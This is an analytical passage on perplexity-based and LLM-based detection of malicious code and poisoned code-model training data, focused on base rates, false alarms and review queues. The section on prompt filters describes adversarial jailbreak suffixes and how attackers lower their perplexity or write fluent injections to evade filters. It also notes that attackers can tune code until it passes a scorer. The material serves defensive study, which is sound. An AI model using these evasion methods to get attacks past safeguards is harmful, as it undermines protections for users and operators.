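A model can also memorise malware that nobody planted in its training data. Security researchers publish malicious code for others to study, and Pianese and colleagues took many of their samples from public collections on GitHub, which supplies much of the training data for code models. If a scoring model has memorised one of these scripts, the script will have a very low perplexity. This too is an inference, since nobody seems to have published a direct test on known malware.

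A memorised script could keep its low score after small changes. The samples in the dataset of Pianese and colleagues average about 396 tokens. If a model gives each token of a memorised script of that length a probability of 0.95, the perplexity is 1.05. If an attacker then adds a new server address of ten tokens, each with a surprise of 4, the perplexity rises only to about 1.16, still far below that of most benign code. Pianese and colleagues found such variants and removed scripts from their dataset that differed only in details like the server address.

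Antivirus programs already detect many exact copies of known malware, so memorisation matters most for altered versions. One way to measure memorisation is to compare similar malware published before and after the scoring model's training cutoff. If the older samples had clearly lower perplexity, the difference would more likely be due to their age than their behaviour. Harmless code may also score as suspicious if it uses a library released after the cutoff.

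### What the model reads before the code

Even with the same scoring model, the score depends on the text that comes before the code. Ashkenazi, Brenner and colleagues (2025), in *Zero-Shot Detection of LLM-Generated Code via Approximated Task Conditioning*, measured this with entropy, which is the surprise that a model should expect at a given position before seeing the next token:

entropy = −Σ p(v) · log p(v)

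Without a task description, average entropy, which is calculated over every possible next token, hardly distinguished AI-written Python from human Python. The AUC under CodeLlama-7B was 0.56 on simple problems and 0.52 on harder ones. The researchers then asked the same model to guess the task from the code, placed its guess before the code and measured the entropy again. The AUC rose to 0.92 and 0.90, almost as high as with the real task descriptions. The AUC for average surprise also rose, from 0.64 to 0.81 on the harder problems under the larger CodeLlama-13B.

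Ashkenazi and colleagues' explanation is that code can be hard to predict because of its purpose or its style. A description reveals the purpose, so the remaining uncertainty is mostly about style. This helps to identify an author but could hinder a search for malware. Given a script that steals documents, a model might describe the task as "Write a script that uploads the user's documents to a server". The upload should then be easy to predict. An attacker could achieve the same effect with a comment at the top of the file. A description from an independent source, such as the program's page in an app store, would be more useful.

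A line's score also depends on the code around it. A call to an upload function is easier to predict if the function's definition appears earlier in the model's input. But a model can process only a limited amount of text at once. The limit was 2,048 tokens for the models that Rubel and colleagues used, so in a long file a suspicious line might be scored without the opening lines that explain what the program is for. Two reviewers using the same model could get different scores for that line if one scored only the function containing it and the other scored the whole file.

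The tokenizer can also change the score, even if two models assign the text the same probability. Suppose both give a line a total surprise of 12. If one splits the line into ten tokens and the other into six, the perplexities are 3.3 and 7.4. Dividing the total surprise by the number of characters instead of tokens removes this difference, but the tokenizer still affects what the model learns.

### Dividing one model's score by another's

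Some text is hard to predict whoever writes it. *DACTYL* (2025) gives the example of a prompt that has GPT-4 write briefly about a capybara working in astrophysics. Hardly any existing text combines those two subjects, so the answer has a high perplexity and a simple detector may misclassify it as human writing. Binoculars, a detector that Hans and colleagues published in 2024, is designed to correct for this with a second model.

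As *CrisisFake* (2026) sets out, Binoculars divides the surprise of the actual text by the surprise one would expect at the same positions. If p is the first model's probability and q the second model's, then

ratio = [average of −log q(actual token)] / [average of −Σ p(v) · log q(v)]

The bottom half of the ratio is called cross-perplexity, although it is an average surprise without the final exponential. It is high where many tokens that are plausible under the first model are improbable under the second. In the capybara answer, both halves should rise, so the ratio changes less than the perplexity does. *From Tokens to Files* says that taking the ratio "cancels much of the prompt-difficulty confound". A low ratio counts as a sign of AI authorship.

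The same correction could reduce false alarms in code. Suppose a new variable name has a surprise of 5.3 where the expected surprise is 5.0. The ratio is 1.06, so the name is about as surprising as expected. In the Linux backdoor, the single `=` might also have a surprise of 5.3, but at a point where the models assigned almost all the probability to a comparison and the expected surprise was only 0.2, which gives a ratio of 26.5. A defender would have to calculate the ratio for each token, because Binoculars averages both values before dividing, and a single token would again have little effect on the averages in a long file.

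The ratio does not help with a bad coding pattern that both models have learned. If both have learned the earlier example's 70–30 split between an insecure line and a safe one, the insecure line has a surprise of 0.36, the safe line has a surprise of 1.20, and the expected surprise is 0.61. The ratio is 0.58 for the insecure line and 1.97 for the safe one, so the insecure line still looks more normal.

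Two very different models might share fewer weaknesses, but the Binoculars formula needs both to assign probabilities to the same set of tokens. According to *VietBinoculars* (2025), Binoculars uses two closely related models with the same tokenizer. Such models are also likely to have similar training data and to predict the same kinds of text poorly. Neither has specifically learned what malicious code looks like, so their ratio is not the likelihood ratio that would give the best test for malice.

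For detecting data poisoning, a more useful comparison would be between a clean model and the same model after training on the suspect data. A defender could look for the examples whose perplexity fell most. Rubel and colleagues scored the poison with both kinds of model but did not report this comparison. Training also lowers the perplexity of legitimate examples, especially ones that occur many times, so the defender would still have to separate planted code from code that people had merely copied.

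## False alarms, base rates and the use of scores for ranking

A detector's trustworthiness depends partly on the base rate, the share of harmful items among everything it checks. Most experiments make harmful code far more common than it is in practice, because a test with one malicious file in a thousand would need a very large number of files. A detector can therefore look precise in a paper and still give its users an unmanageable number of false alarms.

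### Why most alarms are false

If a share α of all items is harmful, then

precision = α · recall / (α · recall + (1 − α) · false positive rate)

Sun and colleagues report that KillBadCode has a recall of 100 percent and an average false positive rate of 8.3 percent. At those rates, if 1 percent of 10,000 examples were poisoned, it would flag all 100 poisoned examples and about 820 clean ones, for a precision of about 11 percent. If only one example in 1,000 were poisoned and both rates stayed the same, it would flag 10 poisoned examples and about 830 clean ones, for a precision of about 1 percent.

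Here is the precision of a detector that never misses a harmful item:

| Harmful items | False positive rate 8.3% | 1% | 0.1% |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 in 10 | 57% | 92% | 99% |
| 1 in 100 | 11% | 50% | 91% |
| 1 in 1,000 | 1.2% | 9% | 50% |
| 1 in 10,000 | 0.1% | 1% | 9% |

In *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, Axelsson (2000) calculated what share of alarms would be real on a small computer network that produces a million log records a day. Two intrusions a day affect ten records each, so one record in 50,000 belongs to an attack. With perfect recall and one false alarm per 100,000 harmless records, two thirds of the alarms would be real. With one false alarm per 1,000, only 2 percent would be. Recall matters much less. If it fell to 70 percent at the lower false alarm rate, 58 percent of the alarms would still be real. The anomaly detectors in Axelsson's comparison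 all had false alarm rates at least ten times too high.

*A Benchmark Comparison of Python Malware Detection Approaches* (Vu, Newman and Meyers, 2022) found equally strict requirements among the administrators of PyPI, the Python package collection. PyPI had about 20,000 new releases a week, and the administrators removed about 20 malicious packages in that time. They were willing to spend some 20 minutes a week on reports, which the real malware alone would use up at a minute per report. They considered even a false positive rate of 0.01 percent, or two false alarms a week, too high. The tools tested had false positive rates of 15 to 97 percent. Even the lowest rate would produce about 3,000 false alarms a week, or 50 hours of reading.

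Later detectors came much closer. *One Detector Fits All* scanned 91,949 PyPI packages over 37 days, with a threshold meant to give a false positive rate of 0.1 percent. Each day it found an average of 2.48 malicious packages and raised an average of 2.18 false alarms. *MalGuard* flagged 144 of 64,348 new packages, and 113 of those 144 were malicious. Most of its false alarms were test demos that used suspicious functions harmlessly. KillBadCode's lowest false positive rate in any test was 0.53 percent, which would still mean more than 100 false alarms a week at PyPI.

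Scoring smaller pieces of code avoids the averaging problem but lowers the base rate. Suppose one file in 1,000 is malicious, each file has 500 lines, and the malicious file contains ten harmful ones. Then one line in 50,000 is harmful. A check that flags 1 percent of ordinary lines would raise about 5,000 false alarms across those files and at most ten correct ones.

### What the absence of an alarm is worth

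When harmful code is rare, nearly everything that passes a check is harmless, even if the check is useless. In Axelsson's network, the chance that a record without an alarm is harmless stays close to 1 whatever the detector's recall. If 99.9 percent of all packages are clean, then finding that 99.9 percent of unflagged packages are clean does not show that the check works.

A better measure is how much the check changes the odds of harm:

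odds without an alarm = odds before the check × (1 − recall) / (1 − false positive rate)

With one harmful package in 1,000 and a false positive rate of 8.3 percent, the results are:

| Recall | Odds multiplied by | Chance that an unflagged package is harmful | Share of unflagged packages that are harmless |
|---|---|---|---|
| 99% | 0.01 | 1 in 92,000 | 99.999% |
| 90% | 0.11 | 1 in 9,200 | 99.99% |
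| 50% | 0.55 | 1 in 1,800 | 99.95% |
| 20% | 0.87 | 1 in 1,100 | 99.91% |
| 0% | 1.09 | 1 in 920 | 99.89% |

The last column hardly changes, even though the check is excellent in the top row and worse than useless in the bottom row. Recall matters most here, and lowering the false positive rate to 1 percent would make little difference.

But recall on past attacks predicts future recall poorly if attackers can choose their scores. Suppose half of all malicious packages come from attackers who test their code against the scoring model until it passes, and the detector catches 90 percent of the rest. Overall recall is then 45 percent, and an unflagged package has a 1 in 1,700 chance of being malicious, down from 1 in 1,000 before the check. About nine in ten of the missed malicious packages come from the attackers who tested their code against the model.

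The packages with the lowest scores, which a reviewer might skip, could even be the most likely to be malicious. An attacker who doesn't know the threshold has a reason to aim well below it. If the half of attackers who adapt all put their packages in the lowest-scoring tenth, at least one package in 200 there would be malicious, five times the overall rate.

### Strange prompts and ordinary ones

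A similar filter for chatbot prompts raised false alarms and missed attacks with low scores. Some attackers try to get a language model to answer a harmful request by adding an adversarial suffix, a string of odd words and symbols that a search program has optimised for this purpose. Alon and Kamfonas (2023), in *Detecting Language Model Attacks with Perplexity*, generated 1,407 such prompts and scored them with GPT-2. Nearly 90 percent had a perplexity above 1,000, and all were above 200 except some dummy prompts whose suffix was just a row of exclamation marks.

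They also scored about 175,000 ordinary prompts, and some had a perplexity ten times higher than the attacks. Many of these were very short, and high scores were common for program code, mathematics, misspellings and languages other than English. Lowering the alarm threshold from 1,000 to 400 reduced the F2-score, which gives recall more weight than precision, from 87.2 to 83.3 percent. A lower threshold cannot reduce recall, so the extra false alarms must have caused the drop.

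Alon and Kamfonas trained a classifier on two numbers, the perplexity of a prompt and its length in tokens. Length helps separate attacks from short, odd questions because an adversarial suffix is added to a complete request, which makes the prompt long. The F2-score rose to 94.2 percent. In the test, the classifier caught 355 of 359 machine-made attacks but none of the 23 human-written ones, because those had about the same perplexity as ordinary text.

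Later work found the same division between readable and unreadable attacks. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that a perplexity threshold worked extremely well against unreadable attacks but poorly against readable ones. In *Breaking the Assumptions* (2026), a perplexity filter flagged none of 3,000 fluent attack prompts at any of five thresholds, although 346 of the prompts succeeded.

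Attackers can also lower the perplexity of the suffixes. In *Baseline Defenses for Adversarial Attacks Against Aligned Language Models* (2023), a search program that gave some weight to low perplexity produced suffixes that almost always passed a filter that scored the whole prompt. Scoring short windows of text separately made the filter harder to evade. According to Alon and Kamfonas, the windowed filter still blocked 80 percent of these attacks, but it also wrongly flagged about 7 percent of ordinary instructions on average.

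### Using anomalies as training examples

The security company Sophos found a use for unusual command lines even when they aren't malicious (Gelman and Bergeron, 2025, *Sophos AI at Black Hat USA ’25*). Command lines are typed instructions that start programs. Sophos collected about 50 million different ones a day, so treating the unusual ones as attacks would have produced far too many false alarms.

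Gelman and Bergeron used anomaly detection to choose examples for training a separate classifier. Three anomaly detectors picked out unusual commands, and another step removed near-duplicates. OpenAI's o3-mini then labelled each remaining command as benign or malicious. Human analysts checked a week of these labels and found the benign ones almost always correct. Gelman and Bergeron added the commands labelled benign to the classifier's training data.

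Adding unusual but harmless commands to the training data raised the classifier's AUC from 0.61 to 0.89 on a difficult set of commands from real incidents. With a simpler starting set, whose labels came from fixed rules, the AUC rose only from 0.71 to 0.77. The added commands helped because the original training data contained mostly common, simple benign commands, so the classifier had mistaken rare and complicated ones for attacks.

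None of the three detectors used perplexity, but perplexity scores could be used in the same way to choose unusual code for labelling. This would help a classifier handle odd but harmless programs. It would help less with malicious code that looks ordinary, because such code would rarely be chosen.

### Models that read and judge code

A language model can also classify a program as malicious or benign directly, which uses more of what the model has learned than a perplexity score does. For *An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages*, Ryan, Khalil and colleagues (2026) assembled 4,070 packages, 370 of them malicious, and tested 13 models. To save money, they measured detection on only 103 files, ten of them malicious, from these packages, using five kinds of prompt and up to three randomness settings.

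Average F1-scores ranged from 0.40 for Gemma 3 4B to 0.99 for GPT-4.1. The models seldom missed malware, with recall below 50 percent in only 1.6 percent of configurations, but precision was below 50 percent in 51 percent of them. When Ryan and colleagues tested which harmful behaviours the models would find in a package, the models often reported one just because the code contained a common function such as `requests.get`.

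Precision would be much lower at a realistic base rate. A model that catches all ten malicious files and wrongly flags ten of the 93 harmless ones has a precision of 50 percent. If only one package in 1,000 were malicious, the same error rates would give a precision of 0.9 percent. GPT-4.1 made no mistakes in eight of its ten configurations, but the sample is too small to establish how reliable it is. A model with a false positive rate of 3 percent could also classify all 93 harmless files correctly, and at PyPI it would raise about 600 false alarms a week.

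Detectors can catch much more malware when they use information from outside the code. Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?*, compared detectors for npm, the main collection of JavaScript packages. Two used the same language model, but the one that first looked up known malware for comparison had a recall 49 percentage points higher than the one that judged the code alone.

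The same study gives another reason to distrust low perplexity. One detector based on statistical features of the code dropped from 87 to 39 percent between 2021 and 2023. Guo and colleagues attribute the drop to attackers moving towards short, simple code that was statistically indistinguishable from harmless packages. About 80 percent of the malware they collected used no evasion technique. They did not measure perplexity, but much of this malware may score low without any effort by the attacker.

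Scanners that use language models can also miss malicious code in files they never analyse. *CASHEWS* (Noirot Ferrand, Adei and colleagues, 2026) tested such scanners on 512 large JavaScript files and found that they analysed only 69 to 86 percent, since many files were too long for the models. One compromised package contained malicious code hidden in a list of more than 1.3 million numbers. A skipped file raises no alarm, so a user could mistake it for a clean one. Removing irrelevant code beforehand raised the share of files analysed to at least 98.8 percent.

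### Three hundred dollars and 1,553 alarms

*MALTOTAL* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a system for checking code at scale. It searches a project for sensitive operations, such as running a command or sending data, extracts the code that leads to each one, and uses a language model, DeepSeek-V3, to classify that code as malicious or benign. In tests on five programming languages, precision was 93 to 98 percent, but between a third and a half of the projects tested were malicious. If malicious projects were rarer and the system's error rates stayed the same, a larger share of the flagged projects would be false alarms for people to review.

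They then scanned 120,000 GitHub projects that another study had singled out for suspicious popularity. The scan cost about $338 and flagged 1,553 projects, which human experts reviewed:

| Result of the review | Projects |
|---|---|
| Malicious and previously unknown | 564 |
| False alarms, such as legitimate remote administration tools | 502 |
| Openly labelled as security research, testing or malware collections | 487 |

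Only 36 percent of the alarms led to a previously unknown malicious project, or 68 percent if the openly labelled projects also count as correct detections. These shares were low because malicious projects were much rarer than in the Python test, even though the false positive rate was also lower, at about 0.4 percent compared with about 4 percent. The openly labelled projects also show that a program's description can matter as much as its code, since the reviewers learned from a README file what the code was for.

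A model's verdict costs less than a third of a cent per project, so saving computing costs is not a strong reason to replace it with a perplexity score. The scarce resource is the experts' time, and a score can help them decide what to read first.

### Putting a review queue in order

A ranking can be useful even when the same score would make a poor verdict. The next table assumes that harmful files are rare and that the scores of harmful and harmless files follow normal distributions with the same spread:

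| AUC | Harmful files in the top 5% of the queue | Harmful files in the bottom half |
|---|---|---|
| 0.50 | 5% | 50% |
| 0.65 | 14% | 29% |
| 0.80 | 32% | 12% |
| 0.95 | 75% | 1% |

DEPA achieved an AUC of 0.80 when it looked for dead code in single files. If 20 of 20,000 releases were malicious, reading the first 1,000 in a ranking with that AUC would uncover six or seven of them, compared with one in a random order. The last 10,000 would still contain two or three. The PyPI administrators, with time for only 20 packages a week, would find roughly one malicious package every two weeks.

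Perplexity is more promising for ordering a list that another tool has narrowed down, as when Ray and colleagues used surprise scores to sort warnings from bug finders. A security team could do the same with packages that a rule has flagged for sending files over the network. The team should compare only programs in the same language and of similar length, since language and length both affect the score.

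### Evidence needed to skip low scorers

Reading low-scoring code last only delays its review, but skipping it requires good evidence that few attacks score low. The evidence needed depends on the costs. If a review costs $10 and would prevent $20,000 of damage from a malicious package, it is worthwhile whenever the package has more than a 1 in 2,000 chance of being malicious. With the base rate and false positive rate used earlier, an unflagged package's chance of being malicious is 1 in 9,200 if the check has 90 percent recall, which is low enough to justify skipping the review, but 1 in 1,800 if recall is 50 percent, which is too high.

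Measuring recall accurately is difficult. To show with 95 percent confidence that a check misses fewer than 1 percent of attacks, a tester would need to run it on about 300 harmful programs and find that it catches every one. The programs should be newer than the scoring model's training data, and some should come from testers who could rewrite their code until it passed the check. Existing malware collections may contain too few ordinary-looking attacks, because they include only what earlier tools and reviewers detected.

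A defender would also have to examine code that the check did not flag. The field tests in *MalGuard* and *MALTOTAL* reviewed only flagged items, so nobody knows how many malicious ones they missed. To show that fewer than one in 10,000 low-scoring packages is malicious, reviewers would have to thoroughly examine about 30,000 of them, chosen at random, and find no malware. PyPI gets about that many releases in a week and a half. Reviewers could spread the work out by examining a small random sample of low-scoring packages every week. If they continued sampling afterwards, they might notice if attackers began to aim for low scores.
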